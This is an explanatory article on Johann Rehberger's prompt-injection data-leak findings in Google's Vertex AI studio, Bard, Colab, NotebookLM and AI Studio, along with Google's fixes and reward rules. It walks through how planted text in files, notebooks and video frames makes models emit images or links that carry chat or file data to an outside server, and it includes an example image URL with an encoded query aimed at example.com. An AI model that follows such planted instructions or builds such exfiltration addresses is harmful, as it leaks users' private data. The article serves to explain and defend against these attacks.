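# Johann Rehberger's prompt injection findings in Google AI Studio, NotebookLM and Colab

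## How displaying an image can leak data, and the first Google cases in 2023

Johann Rehberger is a security researcher who publishes his findings on the blog Embrace The Red. In 2023 and 2024, he showed that hidden text in a document or other file could make several of Google's AI products send a user's private data to an outsider. Security specialists call this data exfiltration. In most of his Google cases, the chat page leaked the data by displaying an image whose web address contained it.

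Rehberger worked in conventional security before he turned to language models. He built red teams, which attack their own employer's systems to find weak points, in Microsoft's Azure Data division and at Uber. The German hacker association Chaos Computer Club (CCC) identifies him in its *Speaker Profile* as Red Team Director at the video game company Electronic Arts. Rehberger's *Trust No AI* (2024) lists eleven systems in which he had found the image leak and reported it to the maker. Five belonged to Google: the chatbot Bard, the developer platform Vertex AI, NotebookLM, AI Studio and Colab. The list also included Microsoft's Bing Chat, OpenAI's ChatGPT and Anthropic's Claude. He called the flaw one of the most common in applications built on language models, but his list includes only his own finds and cannot show how common the flaw was in products he never tested.

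Google AI Studio is a browser tool in which developers try out Google's models before building them into software. A developer writes a system prompt (standing instructions sent to the model with each user message) and chats with the model to test it. At the time of the findings, Google said developers could then export the result as code. Rehberger published data leaks through displayed images in AI Studio in April and August 2024, after reporting leaks in Colab and NotebookLM in late 2023.

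NotebookLM is a research assistant that answers questions from sources the user uploads and cites the passages it relies on, according to Google's *Learn about NotebookLM*. In spring 2024, it accepted Google Docs, PDFs and pasted text, up to 200,000 words per source, and summarized each source as soon as the user added it. At the time, Google advised users not to upload documents with personal or sensitive information. Google renamed the product Gemini Notebook in July 2026 (Woodward, 2026, *NotebookLM is now Gemini Notebook*).

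Colab is a free web service for writing and running Python code in notebooks, which are documents that mix code, results and explanatory text. Google added code generation and a chatbot to it under the name Colab AI. Perry and Basu Mallick (2023) announced those features in *AI-powered coding, free of charge with Colab* and wrote that more than 7 million people had used Colab.

### One prompt for instructions and data

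All three products give a model text from other sources, and the model cannot reliably distinguish that text from its instructions. The application combines the system prompt, the user's question and any document into a single prompt, which the model continues one token (a word or part of a word) at a time.

Prompt injection is text that makes a language model follow an attacker's instructions instead of those of its user or developer. In direct prompt injection, the attacker types the text into the chat, for instance to make the model print its system prompt. In indirect prompt injection, the text is in material that the model reads for the user, such as a document, a notebook or a video. *NEW IMPORTANT INSTRUCTIONS* (Rehberger, 2024), a conference slide deck, distinguishes the two by whether the attacker is the user or a third party. The difference matters for data leaks because a user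 who attacks his own chat mostly sees data he already had, while in an indirect attack the user is the victim and may never see the planted text.

In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, David C, a technical director at the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, describes a recruiter who asks a model to score job applications. One candidate hides a sentence in his CV that tells the model to approve him for interview. The model treats that sentence as an instruction, although the recruiter meant the whole CV as data.

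Prompt injection resembles a database attack in which someone types a command into a form field and the database runs it. Web developers can prevent that attack completely, because a database engine handles commands and stored values differently, and a properly built query keeps the engine from treating a value as a command. David C argued that a language model has no such distinction, because it only predicts the next token. He thought it quite possible that nobody will ever fully prevent prompt injection.

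Developers can partly defend against injection by marking where a document begins and ends, or by labeling it as untrusted. *A Lifecycle and Application-Stack Survey of Large Language Model Vulnerabilities* (2026) rates such marks as useful engineering practice but not a hard security boundary. An experiment in *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion* (Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell, 2026) suggests why. The researchers built probes that measure, from a model's internal state, which speaker the model attributes a passage to. The probes showed that models attributed injected text to the trusted speaker it imitated, however the text was labeled. The researchers then planted fake reasoning, written in the model's own style, in prompts and tool outputs. This attack succeeded 60% of the time against leading models, up from a baseline near zero.

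*On the Inseparability of Instructions and Data in Shared-Embedding Sequence Models* (2026) proves that prompt injection cannot be perfectly prevented in models that represent instructions and data in the same mathematical space, unless something outside that space enforces a separation. Training can still make attacks rarer, and the software around a model can limit what a successful attack achieves.

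Current security advice favors that second option. Coker (2026) reported in *Prompt Injection Remains Biggest LLM Risk, Despite Limited Incidents* that the Open Worldwide Application Security Project (OWASP), a non-profit that ranks software risks, again put prompt injection first in August 2026. It would not have made the top ten on recorded incidents alone. OWASP explained that few clean exploits reach public databases because security teams fight prompt injection hard, which is plausible but hard to check. It mainly recommended assuming that attackers will get past the model, and restricting what the model may do and where its output may go. In the image leak, the output goes to a web browser.

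### From planted text to a server log

Most chat pages turn Markdown, a simple text notation, into formatted text, links and images. When a model writes a picture's address in Markdown, the browser fetches the picture from the server in that address so the page can show it. The address can also carry extra text after the file name. Data can leak if an outsider gets the model to combine these ordinary web features.

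In a hypothetical attack, a user asks an assistant, "Is the merger off?" Later in the same chat, she pastes in a supplier's report and asks for a summary. The supplier has hidden instructions in the report, in white text on a white page, to end the answer with an image whose address contains her earlier question.

1. The planted passage enters the prompt along with the rest of the report.
2. The model follows it and writes, after the summary, an image with the address `example.com/dot.png?q=Is%20the%20merger%20off%3F`.
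3. The chat page recognises the notation and creates an image at that spot.
4. The browser asks the server at example.com for the file, and sends the whole address in doing so.
5. The server logs the request, as web servers routinely do, and the supplier reads the question in the log.

The odd characters in the address come from a standard encoding. An address can't contain spaces, and a question mark separates the file from the extra text. The model therefore replaces each space in that text with `%20` and the question mark with `%3F`. Anyone can quickly reverse these replacements.

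The model needs no internet connection, because the user's browser makes the request. The leak works even if the server doesn't send back a real picture, because the data arrives with the request. What can leak depends on what the prompt contains, which may include earlier messages, an uploaded document and perhaps the system prompt. If the data is too long to fit comfortably in a URL, the attacker can have the model summarise it first.

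### Clicks and Content Security Policies

This kind of image leak is zero-click because the user does not have to do anything after the model answers, although she did have to bring the report into the chat. If the page shows links but not images, an attacker can instead use a one-click leak, in which the model puts the data into a link's address and the user has to click it. Rehberger found one in Microsoft 365 Copilot in February 2024. A phishing email made the assistant search the victim's inbox and write what it found into a link in invisible characters. Microsoft fixed the flaw in July 2024. One-click leaks are less reliable for the attacker, but a link in an assistant's answer looks trustworthy, and its visible text need not reveal the address.

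A website can block the image version of this leak with a Content Security Policy (CSP), a rule that tells the browser which domains it may load images and other content from. The current draft of the standard is W3C's *Content Security Policy Level 3* (2026). The part of the rule that covers images is called img-src, according to MDN's *CSP* reference page. When a page requests content from a domain the rule doesn't allow, the browser blocks the request and reports an error. Google's web.dev guide *Content security policy* shows this for scripts.

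If the chat page in the invented case had sent a policy that allowed images only from its own domain, the browser would not have contacted example.com. The model would still have followed the supplier's instructions, and the user might have noticed a broken image under her summary, but no data would have reached the supplier's log. However, an image policy does not restrict links. It also fails if an attacker can receive data through a domain it allows, a weakness that Rehberger exploited in Bard in September 2023.

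### Generative AI Studio in Vertex AI

About three weeks before he reported the Bard leak, Rehberger told Google that displayed images could leak data in Generative AI Studio, a tool inside Vertex AI, which was Google Cloud's machine learning platform. Generative AI Studio is a different product from Google AI Studio, and Google opened it to everyone with a Google Cloud account in May 2023 (Yang, 2023, *Google Cloud advances generative AI at I/O*). Developers used it to adjust Google's models and to test how a model answered particular prompts (SiliconANGLE, 2023). Google has since absorbed Vertex AI, a change that Google Cloud's *Gemini Enterprise Agent Platform release notes* (2026) date to 22 April 2026.

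The studio rendered Markdown images in a model's answers. Embrace The Red's *Google Cloud Vertex AI* post describes how Rehberger instructed the model to write an image whose address contained a summary of the conversation so far. When the page displayed the image, the browser contacted his server, which received the summary, correctly encoded. He also found that he could leave the image's description empty. This made the image about as conspicuous as a single pixel, so a user would have been unlikely to notice it.

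Rehberger reported the flaw privately to Google on 30 August 2023 and published his findings after Google had fixed it, a practice called responsible disclosure. Google's security team accepted the report as a genuine issue 22 minutes later. On 16 September he received a reward from Google's Vulnerability Reward Program (VRP), which pays outsiders for reporting flaws. On 19 October he asked about progress, and Google confirmed that a fix was in place.

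Fifty days passed between the report and that confirmation, but the fix probably took less time. Rehberger suspected that Google had fixed the leak a few weeks before he asked, perhaps around the date of the reward. His later slides are consistent with this, as they include a table of the situation in September 2023 that lists Vertex AI as fixed. The same table lists Microsoft, Anthropic and Discord as having fixed their versions of the leak, and OpenAI as having declined to fix ChatGPT's.

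As far as Rehberger could tell from outside, Google had stopped AI Studio from displaying links and images at all. A model's answer could still contain the markup for an image, but the page showed it as plain text, so the browser didn't fetch anything. This blocked data leaks through links, which needed one click, and through images, which needed none, though the model remained as open to prompt injection as before. Rehberger wrote on his blog, Embrace The Red, that this was probably the best possible fix for security, at least for a tool that doesn't need images.

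Rehberger rated the flaw medium severity because AI Studio did not yet have integrations that could pull in web pages, emails or shared files. An attacker had to rely on a user pasting untrusted text into the prompt, which Rehberger considered fairly common, or possibly on a customer training a model on tainted data. Google classed the report as an abuse-related methodology with high impact and low likelihood, which Rehberger found reasonable. Both ratings reflected the difficulty of getting hostile text in front of the model, not doubt that the leak worked, and that difficulty could change as soon as Google connected a chatbot to its users' files.

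### Bard and Google Apps Script

Bard, Google's chatbot for the general public, had just made that connection. Its new Extensions could read a user's Gmail, Drive and Docs, so an attacker could deliver planted text by sharing a document. Embrace The Red's *Hacking Google Bard* post describes how Rehberger, with help from the researchers Joseph Thacker and Kai Greshake, got Bard to write the image, but Google's CSP stopped the browser from loading it from his server. The policy did allow `*.google.com` and `*.googleusercontent.com`, where the asterisk covers every subdomain, as a guide by the coding-education organisation CodePath explains. Google Apps Script lets the public write small programs that run at addresses on those domains. Rehberger wrote one that copied any data sent in its address into his own Google Doc, and set it to answer requests without a login. Loading the image from that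 program sent part of the user's chat to an outsider without violating the policy. He reported the leak on 19 September 2023, three days after the Vertex AI reward, and Google confirmed a fix on 19 October. The CSP had not changed and Bard still displayed images, so Rehberger guessed that Google had begun to filter data out of their addresses.

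## Colab and NotebookLM: two reports from late 2023 and their repairs

On 29 November 2023, about six weeks after Google confirmed the Bard fix, Rehberger reported an image leak in Colab AI, the assistant inside Google's notebook service. Google was still rolling the assistant out. According to Google's *Release notes* for Colab, the AI coding features reached paying subscribers in more regions on 27 November and users of every tier in 175 locales on 18 December.

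### An instruction not to display images

Rehberger began by getting the assistant to reveal its system prompt. Embrace The Red's *Google Colab AI* (2024) recounts that the prompt included an instruction not to render images. He did not know why Google had included the instruction, but wrote that it could not work if it was meant to prevent data leaks.

His argument depends on the idea of a trust boundary, the point in a system where software checks input instead of trusting it. A web server, for example, checks a visitor's password before it shows an account. A language model has no such boundary between the system prompt and the other text it receives, so Rehberger regarded system instructions as suggestions that an attacker can override.

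The same reasoning applies to secrets. Some developers put sensitive information in a system prompt because they assume users can't see it. Rehberger wrote in *Trust No AI* that users can often retrieve it easily, and gave the leak of Bing Chat's system prompt as an example. He also recommended Gandalf, a game by the security company Lakera in which players try to talk a chatbot into revealing a secret. He advised developers to keep sensitive data out of the system prompt altogether.

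An instruction like Colab's may still help, since it can make a model less likely to display images in ordinary conversation. But an attacker can keep rewording a request until it works.

The version that worked for Rehberger gave the model several short fragments of text and asked it to join them, without mentioning images. None of the fragments was an image address, but together they formed the Markdown for an image on his server, with a placeholder at the end of the address. The prompt told the model to replace the placeholder with the previous chat message and to write each space as a plus sign, another common way to encode spaces in an address. It also asked for ordinary text instead of a code block. A chat page shows the contents of a code block exactly as written, so the browser would not have fetched the image. The model complied, and when the page displayed the image, the browser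 sent the previous message to Rehberger's server.

Rehberger did not analyze why the fragments worked. A likely reason is that a rule against images affects a text-joining task only if the model detects that the joined text will display an image. A Content Security Policy works without that detection, as does a chat page that leaves image notation as plain text. Rehberger showed only one example. He called the bypass quick to find, but he gave no success rate and did not say whether a plain request for an image would have failed.

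### Reporting a flaw before it became serious

In November 2023, Colab AI did not read the user's open notebook, so an attacker had to persuade the user to paste hostile text into the chat. Rehberger considered the flaw low severity for that reason.

Rehberger reported the leak immediately because he was certain that Google would eventually add the notebook's content to the prompt. An attacker could then plant instructions in a notebook and get a user to open it, which would make the leak high severity. He explained this in his report to Google.

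Google confirmed the leak, fixed it and closed the ticket in January 2024, between one and two months after the report, but did not pay a reward. In September it had paid Rehberger for the Vertex AI leak, which also depended mainly on pasted text. He later complained that Google had assessed, fixed and rewarded similar findings differently, which he saw as a sign that the industry had not yet agreed on how such products should behave. Embrace The Red does not report a reason from Google, but severity may explain the difference, since Rehberger had rated the Vertex AI leak medium and the Colab leak low.

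A researcher in his position has a financial reason to wait, because a more serious flaw is more likely to earn a reward. Rehberger still thought he was right to report early, since waiting could have exposed Colab users to a zero-click leak.

### One customer's record exposes another's

NotebookLM was designed to read the user's files, which Rehberger expected Colab to do in the future. He reported a data leak through image rendering in NotebookLM on 4 December 2023, five days after his Colab report.

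Embrace The Red's *Bobby Tables but with LLM Apps* takes its title from an xkcd web comic in which a mother gives her son a name that contains a database command. When his school enters the name, it loses its student records. Rehberger applied the idea to a customer list. Customers can usually edit their own details, such as a name or profile description, so one of them could write a prompt injection there and wait for an employee to load the list into NotebookLM. The attacker would not need to send the employee anything or have access to any other customer's record.

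To test this, Rehberger made a Google Doc with a small table of customers. One row listed a customer called Johann, with his email address and a code. In the row below, the description field for a customer called Sarah held the planted text. It used the same trick with fragments as in Colab, but this time it was meant to put Johann's email address and code into the image's address.

Rehberger then acted as the employee and made two requests that would be ordinary for someone reading a customer list. He first asked NotebookLM to show the customers, and the answer included a message that the injection had succeeded. This answer leaked nothing, but the model was already following text from the file. When he then asked it to show Sarah, the answer included the image, and the browser sent Johann's details to Rehberger's server without a click.

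He also noticed that NotebookLM displayed images in its source preview pane, apparently without involving the model. An image there could reveal to an outsider that someone had opened the file. It could not collect data from other records, because the attacker would have to write the image's full URL in advance.

### Sales figures from a second document

The customer test did not show whether an attacker could reach data outside the file with the planted text. Rehberger therefore tried two documents, one with internal sales information and one with the customer list. The planted text contained a request for the sales numbers for the USA and Germany, and the browser sent them in the image's address.

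NotebookLM's design helps explain this result. Simon Willison, the programmer who coined the term "prompt injection", called the product in effect a tool for building retrieval-augmented generation chatbots (Willison, 2024, *Google NotebookLM Data Exfiltration*). In such a chatbot, software finds relevant passages in the user's files and adds them to the prompt. If passages from two files end up in the same prompt, instructions in one can refer to data in the other.

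Rehberger rated the NotebookLM leak high severity because of this second test. The attack was somewhat easier in the test than it would be in practice, since he had set up both documents and knew what to ask for. A real attacker would have to guess what else the user had uploaded, or ask for something general, such as the summary Rehberger had obtained from Vertex AI.

The attack worked consistently when Rehberger reported it, but less reliably when he tried it again a few days before publishing. He did not explain the change or give figures. Lower reliability would have protected users only partly, because the planted text stays in the file and any later question about the file may trigger the attack.

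Rehberger also pointed out that an attacker could use planted text to make the model add invented rows to a table or leave out real ones, which no restriction on images would prevent. In *Trust No AI* he suggested that applications cite their sources and mark any text they copy verbatim. NotebookLM already cited passages, which helps a user catch an invented row, but a missing row is harder to notice because there is no citation to check.

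### Publication after 132 days

Google confirmed the NotebookLM flaw but had not fixed it by mid-April 2024. Rehberger then published his findings, 132 days after reporting the flaw. He cited an industry norm that researchers may publish if a company does not fix a flaw within a reasonable time, which he put at three to four months.

Publishing the post carried a risk because it included the planted text and a link to the demonstration document, which let readers reproduce a leak that still worked. But it also gave NotebookLM's users a chance to be careful, after they had spent more than four months uploading files without knowing about the flaw.

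The Google Labs team, which ran NotebookLM, contacted Rehberger directly after he published. Willison dates the fix to 18 April, and Rehberger announced it in an update dated 19 April, probably a day after Google deployed it. By Willison's date, Google needed 136 days in total, about four of them after publication. The timing suggests that the publicity made Google act, although the company may already have been working on a fix. It had closed the Vertex AI leak within 50 days and the Bard leak within 30.

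With his original report, Rehberger had recommended to Google that NotebookLM not display images from arbitrary domains or clickable links to them. He warned that a planted link could prompt the user to sign in again and leak data when clicked. Willison considered an attack of this kind possible whenever a language model reads untrusted text, and he advised developers to take great care with Markdown images and even with outbound links. The fix Rehberger announced in April covered images, and his update did not mention any change to links.

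He advised users, as Google already did, not to process sensitive information in NotebookLM, and to keep out data from untrusted sources. Either precaution would have prevented the leak he demonstrated, which required both hostile text and sensitive information. But people used NotebookLM to read documents, and some useful documents are sensitive. Untrusted sources can also be hard to recognize, since an employee would normally think of the customer list as the company's own file.

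### Links in Colab after the image fix

Rehberger's prediction about Colab came true in 2024. The assistant, which Google had renamed Gemini in Colab, began automatically adding the open notebook's content to the prompt. Rehberger described the change a few weeks later in a post published on or before 13 August 2024, when the security company Adversa AI summarized it in its newsletter, *LLM Security Top Digest*.

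An attacker could now plant instructions in a notebook and share it. People often work with notebooks that someone else wrote, and Google had made this easier in January 2024 by letting users of the data science site Kaggle open its notebooks in Colab with one click. A stranger's notebook is already risky because its code may send data out when the user runs it. Prompt injection created a risk even for a cautious user who only asked the assistant what the notebook did.

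Google had stopped images from leaking data before notebook content entered the prompt. Without that fix, a shared notebook could have sent out a user's code without a click. This supports Rehberger's decision to report early, although Google might have found the leak itself while preparing the new feature.

Links could still leak data. Colab routed every clickable link in an answer through a Google address that asks the user to confirm before it opens an outside website, but anyone who continues still sends whatever data the link contains. Rehberger found that the confirmation page did not appear for links to Google's own domains. Google Apps Script programs run on those domains, and he had already used one to collect data from Bard.

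Rehberger demonstrated a one-click leak with a notebook containing planted text that made the assistant talk like a pirate. The assistant asked the user for personal information and then offered a link. When Rehberger clicked it, his program received the name and email address from the chat, along with the notebook's source code. The pirate talk made the injection obvious to anyone watching, but a real attacker would presumably have the assistant behave normally and present the link as something useful.

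Rehberger also inspected the prompt to see what else could leak. It contained the chat history and the notebook's code, but not the output of its cells, the blocks of code that a user runs one at a time. A notebook that loaded and printed a table of patients would therefore have exposed its code, but not the printed rows. Code can be sensitive too, especially if it contains passwords or access keys. In November 2023, Google had launched a separate store for private keys, called Secrets, which let users keep them out of their code.

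A link can harm a user without carrying any data. In another version of the attack, the assistant offered a link to a Google Meet video call, where a scammer could be waiting. Rehberger describes the same trick against Gemini in Google Drive. Amazon's assistant Amazon Q for Business leaked data through links, and Amazon chose the stricter remedy of no longer displaying them. Removing links would have inconvenienced Colab's users more, because programmers often want links to documentation.

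### Colab since 2024

It is unclear whether Google has since changed how Colab treats links to Google's own domains. Google's *Release notes* up to August 2025 list no change to links in the assistant's answers. This is only weak evidence that nothing changed, because the notes also omit the image fix and the addition of notebook content to the prompt.

Other changes have given the assistant more access to the user's work. Google's *Fully Reimagined* announced a version that can rewrite a whole notebook on request. Google's *Supercharge your notebooks* describes an agent that makes a plan, runs code and reasons about the results. Google opened this agent to all users in summer 2025. The agent must receive those results in some form, so the limit that kept cell outputs out of the prompt in 2024 may no longer hold. In August 2025, Google added a switch that turns off the AI features in a single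 notebook. Instructors had asked for it so that students could work without help, but users can also use it to remove the assistant from a notebook they don't trust.

Shumway and LaPresta (2026) announced in *Introducing Learn Mode* that notebook authors can write custom instructions for Gemini and store them in the notebook. If those instructions stay in the notebook when its author shares it, Gemini will, by design, receive instructions from someone other than its user. The presence of such instructions would then no longer be a sign of an attack, so Google would have to limit what they can make Gemini do.

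## AI Studio: image leaks published in April and August 2024

Rehberger published two posts about image leaks in Google AI Studio in 2024. *Trust No AI* lists the first as *Google AI Studio Data Exfiltration via Prompt Injection - Possible Regression and Fix*. A regression is a fault in a new version of software that an earlier version did not have. The title suggests that Rehberger thought AI Studio had once been free of the leak, and that Google then fixed it.

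According to Embrace The Red's *Google AI Studio*, the post about the second leak, users could upload an entire folder at the time of the first post. The later post calls the first finding "Mass Data Exfiltration", presumably because one hostile file could expose everything else in the folder. By August Google had removed folder uploads, but users could still upload many files at once as a zip file. Rehberger tested AI Studio again and found that displayed images could again send data to an outsider.

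### A summary of every employee's review

In the August demonstration, someone at a company uploads a set of performance reviews and asks Gemini, Google's model, to analyze them. The user doesn't know that a file called Johann.txt contains planted text.

That text instructed the model to write one image for each file in the chat. Each image's address pointed to Rehberger's server and had two labeled fields, one for the file's name and one for a 60-word summary of its contents. The text also instructed the model to write spaces as plus signs, avoid a code block, end with a line announcing that Johann had been there, and write nothing else. When the page displayed the images, the browser requested each one separately, sending the server the file name and summary of one review at a time.

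The instruction in Johann.txt covered every file in the chat, whatever its name or contents, so an attacker could use it without knowing how many colleagues had reviews in the zip file. The file names would probably show whose review each summary described. In the NotebookLM test, Rehberger had to ask for particular sales figures, so he needed some idea of what the second document contained.

Sending one request per file also gets more data out. Browsers and servers limit the length of a web address, which limits how much text one image request can carry. If an upload contained 30 reviews and each request carried a 60-word summary, the attacker would get about 1,800 words. A single request would have to cover all 30 reviews in 60 words, or two words per person. The attacker wouldn't get the full reviews, and the model could summarize them incorrectly, but 60 words are enough for a rating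 and the main criticism.

Rehberger used a transparent, one-pixel image because thirty visible pictures in an answer would make a user suspicious. The image's size does not affect how much data it leaks. Returning a valid image also avoids the broken-image symbol that a browser may show when a picture fails to load. In Vertex AI, Rehberger had made the image inconspicuous by leaving its description empty.

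In the attack as Rehberger published it, a user who had asked for an analysis would have received only an odd line about Johann, because the planted text told the model to write nothing else. This would also have revealed that something was wrong, but only after the data had left. A real attacker would presumably let the model write the analysis as well. Rehberger did not say how often the attack worked.

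### HTML tags and the missing Content Security Policy

When Rehberger began retesting AI Studio, he tried Markdown images again, but they worked only sporadically. He then had the model write an HTML image tag, which makes a browser load a picture. This greatly simplified the attack, because he could request the tag by name in the planted text. In Colab and NotebookLM, he had made the model assemble a Markdown image from harmless-looking fragments.

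Markdown images and HTML image tags make the browser send the same request. A chat page converts a Markdown image into an HTML tag before the browser acts on it, but no conversion is needed if the model writes the tag itself. Rehberger showed both forms side by side in his April 2024 slides.

Rehberger did not explain why the HTML image tag worked better. Google's first fix may have changed how the page converted Markdown to HTML, blocking most Markdown images but letting through tags that needed no conversion. Alternatively, the model may have become less likely to write Markdown images with outside addresses, but not less likely to write tags with them. Markdown images still worked occasionally, which suggests that they were not completely blocked.

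Rehberger was also unsure how the flaw had arisen. He described it as an apparent regression or bypass (a way around a fix that is still in place), but said the behavior might have existed all along, because AI Studio did not yet have a Content Security Policy (CSP) to stop the browser from loading images from arbitrary domains.

These explanations partly overlap. If the first fix covered only Markdown, HTML tags could have leaked data both before and after it, and the August attack would have bypassed the fix through an old flaw. The page had no CSP telling the browser to block such images, so a gap in the page's own image handling was enough for a leak, but this doesn't show which explanation is right. Rehberger couldn't determine that from outside, because users of a website can't test its earlier versions.

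Companies catch regressions by repeating old attacks after each update, but a test using only Markdown images would have missed the HTML tag. A Content Security Policy (CSP) covers both, because the browser checks the address of every image, however the model wrote it. Google already had such a policy in Bard in September 2023. It blocked Rehberger's first attempt, but he then found a way through Google's own domains, so a policy for AI Studio would have needed to exclude those domains too.

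OpenAI's repair to ChatGPT was also incomplete. The company had introduced a check on image addresses, but the mobile apps were still vulnerable in December 2023, and the macOS app released in 2024 also lacked the check. Rehberger found that planted text could store instructions in ChatGPT's long-term memory, making ChatGPT continuously send out the user's conversations. OpenAI's repair did not cover all of its apps, while AI Studio's probably did not cover every notation for images.

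### Instructions in the frames of a video

Rehberger also triggered the AI Studio leak with a video. He had previously hidden instructions in the transcripts of YouTube videos, which a model reads as ordinary text, but this time he put the instructions in the video's frames as text. Gemini read them while analyzing the video and followed them, as it had followed the text in Johann.txt. Rehberger did not report how long the words had to stay on screen or how reliably the attack worked.

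A company could search uploaded documents for suspicious wording before giving them to a model, but an attacker can often evade this by rephrasing the text. To search a video the same way, software must first extract the words from the frames. A user could watch the video for planted instructions, but people often give a model a long video to avoid watching it.

Viewers could see the words in Rehberger's frames. *Weaponizing image scaling against production AI systems* (Trail of Bits, 2025) describes a later attack that hid instructions in still images. Many AI systems shrink large images before passing them to a model. Trail of Bits, a security company, prepared pictures whose instructions appeared only after shrinking, so the user saw a harmless picture while the model received a command. The company used this method to extract data through Gemini CLI, Google's command-line assistant, and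 also exploited image scaling in Vertex AI Studio, Google Assistant and Gemini's web interface.

Both attacks make it harder to follow the usual advice to keep untrusted material away from a chatbot. Looking at a file may not reveal the instructions in it, so a user can only judge the file by where it came from.

### A public message and a fix within 24 hours

Google's official channel for security reports gave Rehberger no date for a fix, so he tagged Logan Kilpatrick of Google in a message on X. According to Embrace The Red, Kilpatrick replied on 7 August 2024 that he was working on it, and Google fixed the leak within 24 hours. AI Studio then showed image tags as text, as Vertex AI's Generative AI Studio had since its 2023 fix.

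The 24 hours count from the public message. Rehberger's post does not give the date of his original report, so the total time is unknown and can't be fairly compared with that for NotebookLM, which was still leaking after 132 days. But in both cases a fix came within days after Rehberger went public and was in contact with people outside the security intake. Showing a tag as text is also a small change. These facts suggest that Google's delays came more from priorities, or from getting a report to the right team, than from the difficulty of the fix. However, the security intake may have already passed on the AI Studio report, and engineers may have been about to act.

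Willison (2024) reprinted the planted text in *Google AI Studio data exfiltration demo* on 7 August, the day of Kilpatrick's reply, so readers may have been able to reproduce the leak for some hours before Google closed it.

Rehberger did not mention Google adding a CSP. If Google had not added one, AI Studio's users still depended on the page to recognize every way a model could write an image.

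Other companies have mostly responded in a similar way. GitHub, for example, fixed its programming assistant Copilot Chat in June 2024 by disabling Markdown images from untrusted domains, Willison reported. A year later, Willison's *The lethal trifecta for AI agents* listed AI Studio among 14 products and features in which he had seen prompt injection lead to data leaks between April 2023 and February 2025. He wrote that the makers had promptly fixed almost all of them, usually by blocking the route the data took out. His list includes NotebookLM, so either it was one of the exceptions or he was using "promptly" loosely.

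### How would the attacker know?

Willison also posted about the AI Studio leak on Mastodon, where a reader, Colby Russell, doubted that it was an attack. Russell first thought the attacker had supplied both the planted text and the other files, and so could only steal data he already had. Willison explained that the victim supplies the private files and adds the malicious one without realizing what it contains.

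Russell then raised the better objection that the victim prepares the zip file, so the attacker has to expect her to give a vulnerable AI tool a collection of documents that includes text he controls. Willison agreed, and said this made the attack relatively unlikely to affect most people. He thought the flaw still mattered, especially because there was an obvious fix, which was not to display images from external domains. Google had judged the Vertex AI leak similarly, rating its impact high and its likelihood low.

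Willison argues that even a small risk is worth removing if the fix is easy, and Google's quick repair supports him on that point. A tool for testing models loses little by showing an outside image as text. The argument would be weaker for a product whose users need such images.

The objection also applies less to some attackers than to others. A stranger has little reason to expect a particular person to upload his document to AI Studio. An employee who contributes to his own performance review can expect someone to read it along with his colleagues' reviews, and may know that his manager uses AI for such work. He doesn't need to know when. If she never uploads the files, the attack fails, although she may find the planted text. The customer in the NotebookLM demonstration was in a similar position.

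The likelihood of an attack also depends on the product. Willison pointed out to Russell that people also run language models on incoming email, text collected from websites and Google Docs that others have shared with them. In those cases an attacker can get text to the model by sending a message or sharing a file, without waiting for someone to assemble a zip file.

AI Studio had become a more likely place for an attack by August 2024 because it was the only way to try a new experimental version of Gemini 1.5 Pro. That model led the LMSYS Arena, a public ranking based on users' votes between models' answers. Willison thought this made people more likely to be processing real data in AI Studio instead of just developing software with it, though he gave no usage figures. If he was right, people were putting sensitive files into a tool Google had built for experiments, and Google had made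 a leak more serious by releasing the model there, even though it hadn't changed how the tool displayed images.

Rehberger demonstrated the AI Studio leak with his own files and reported no real victims. His later essay *The Normalization of Deviance in AI*, which Willison discussed in December 2025, argues that AI companies confuse the absence of a successful attack with robust security. It borrows Diane Vaughan's term for organizations that ignore safety rules without consequence and come to regard this as normal. An image leak is also hard to rule out, because it adds only one request to the many that any web page causes the victim's browser to make, and the clearest record of what the browser sent is on the attacker's server.

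## How Google classed, rewarded and defended against such reports up to 2026

Google called the Vertex AI leak an abuse-related methodology, which is one of Google's own categories. Google's *What is an abuse risk?* defines an abuse risk as a product feature that can cause unexpected damage when used in an unexpected way. The example is a social network app that shows users which of their contacts have joined. If the app doesn't limit lookups, a spammer can use the feature to build a large database of targets.

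Google describes a security vulnerability as a loophole that needs a fix, and an abuse risk as often inherent in a feature. For abuse risks, it therefore often keeps the feature and tries to prevent abuse at scale. An image leak fits both descriptions, because a chat page displays images on purpose but an attacker can use them to collect private data. Google treated the Vertex AI leak as both, rating the report as abuse but removing the feature.

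Google classed each incoming report as a security vulnerability, a significant abuse risk or a non-issue. Its Trust & Safety specialists assessed the possible abuse risks. They considered only attacks that could be scaled up or that affected privacy, and their most common reason for rejecting a report was that they thought the attack wasn't severe enough.

### Rewards under the abuse rules

The reward for an abuse risk depended on its impact and its probability. Google's *Abuse Vulnerability Reward Program Rules* set these amounts in early 2025:

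| | High impact | Medium impact | Low impact |
|---|---|---|---|
| High probability | up to $13,337 | $3,133.70 to $5,000 | $1,337 |
| Medium probability | $3,133.70 to $5,000 | $1,337 | $100 to $500 |
| Low probability | $1,337 | $100 to $500 | public credit only |

Impact covered privacy violations, financial loss and the number of users at risk. Probability covered what the attacker needed beforehand and how likely the victim was to notice. The Vertex AI leak had high impact and low probability, so by this table it would have earned $1,337, about a tenth of the top amount. Rehberger did not publish what he received, and the amounts may have been different in 2023. The table may also explain why his Colab report earned nothing, since a flaw with low impact and low probability earned credit but no money.

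Google (2023) first published detailed criteria for AI reports on 26 October 2023, a week after it confirmed the Vertex AI and Bard fixes. A prompt injection qualified if it was invisible to the victim and changed the victim's account or assets, or if it affected a tool whose answers were used to make decisions about users. Google excluded issues it already knew about and jailbreaks, in which a user gets a model to produce forbidden content in their own session.

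An image leak copies data without changing the account, so it does not clearly fit either of Google's descriptions of a qualifying injection. Google also listed two kinds of data extraction, but they concerned a model's training data and its internal design. A researcher reporting an image leak had to rely on a general clause that admitted any valid security or abuse issue. The same criteria were still in the rules in early 2025, although Google had by then fixed at least five image leaks that Rehberger reported.

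### Injections that Google left open

Rehberger's first report about Google's AI features in Docs, on 22 June 2023, described a scam risk rather than a data leak. Embrace the Red's *Google Docs AI Features* describes a document with hidden text that made the AI replace its summary with a false malware warning and a phone number that a scammer could answer. Google closed the report within weeks as "Won't Fix (Intended Behavior)". In Tom's Hardware's *Google Docs AI Open to Prompt Injection Attacks*, a Google spokesperson pointed to the security protections built into Docs. Rehberger thought the impact was probably limited at the time but expected it to grow as Google added features. In December 2024, he still listed the issue as unresolved.

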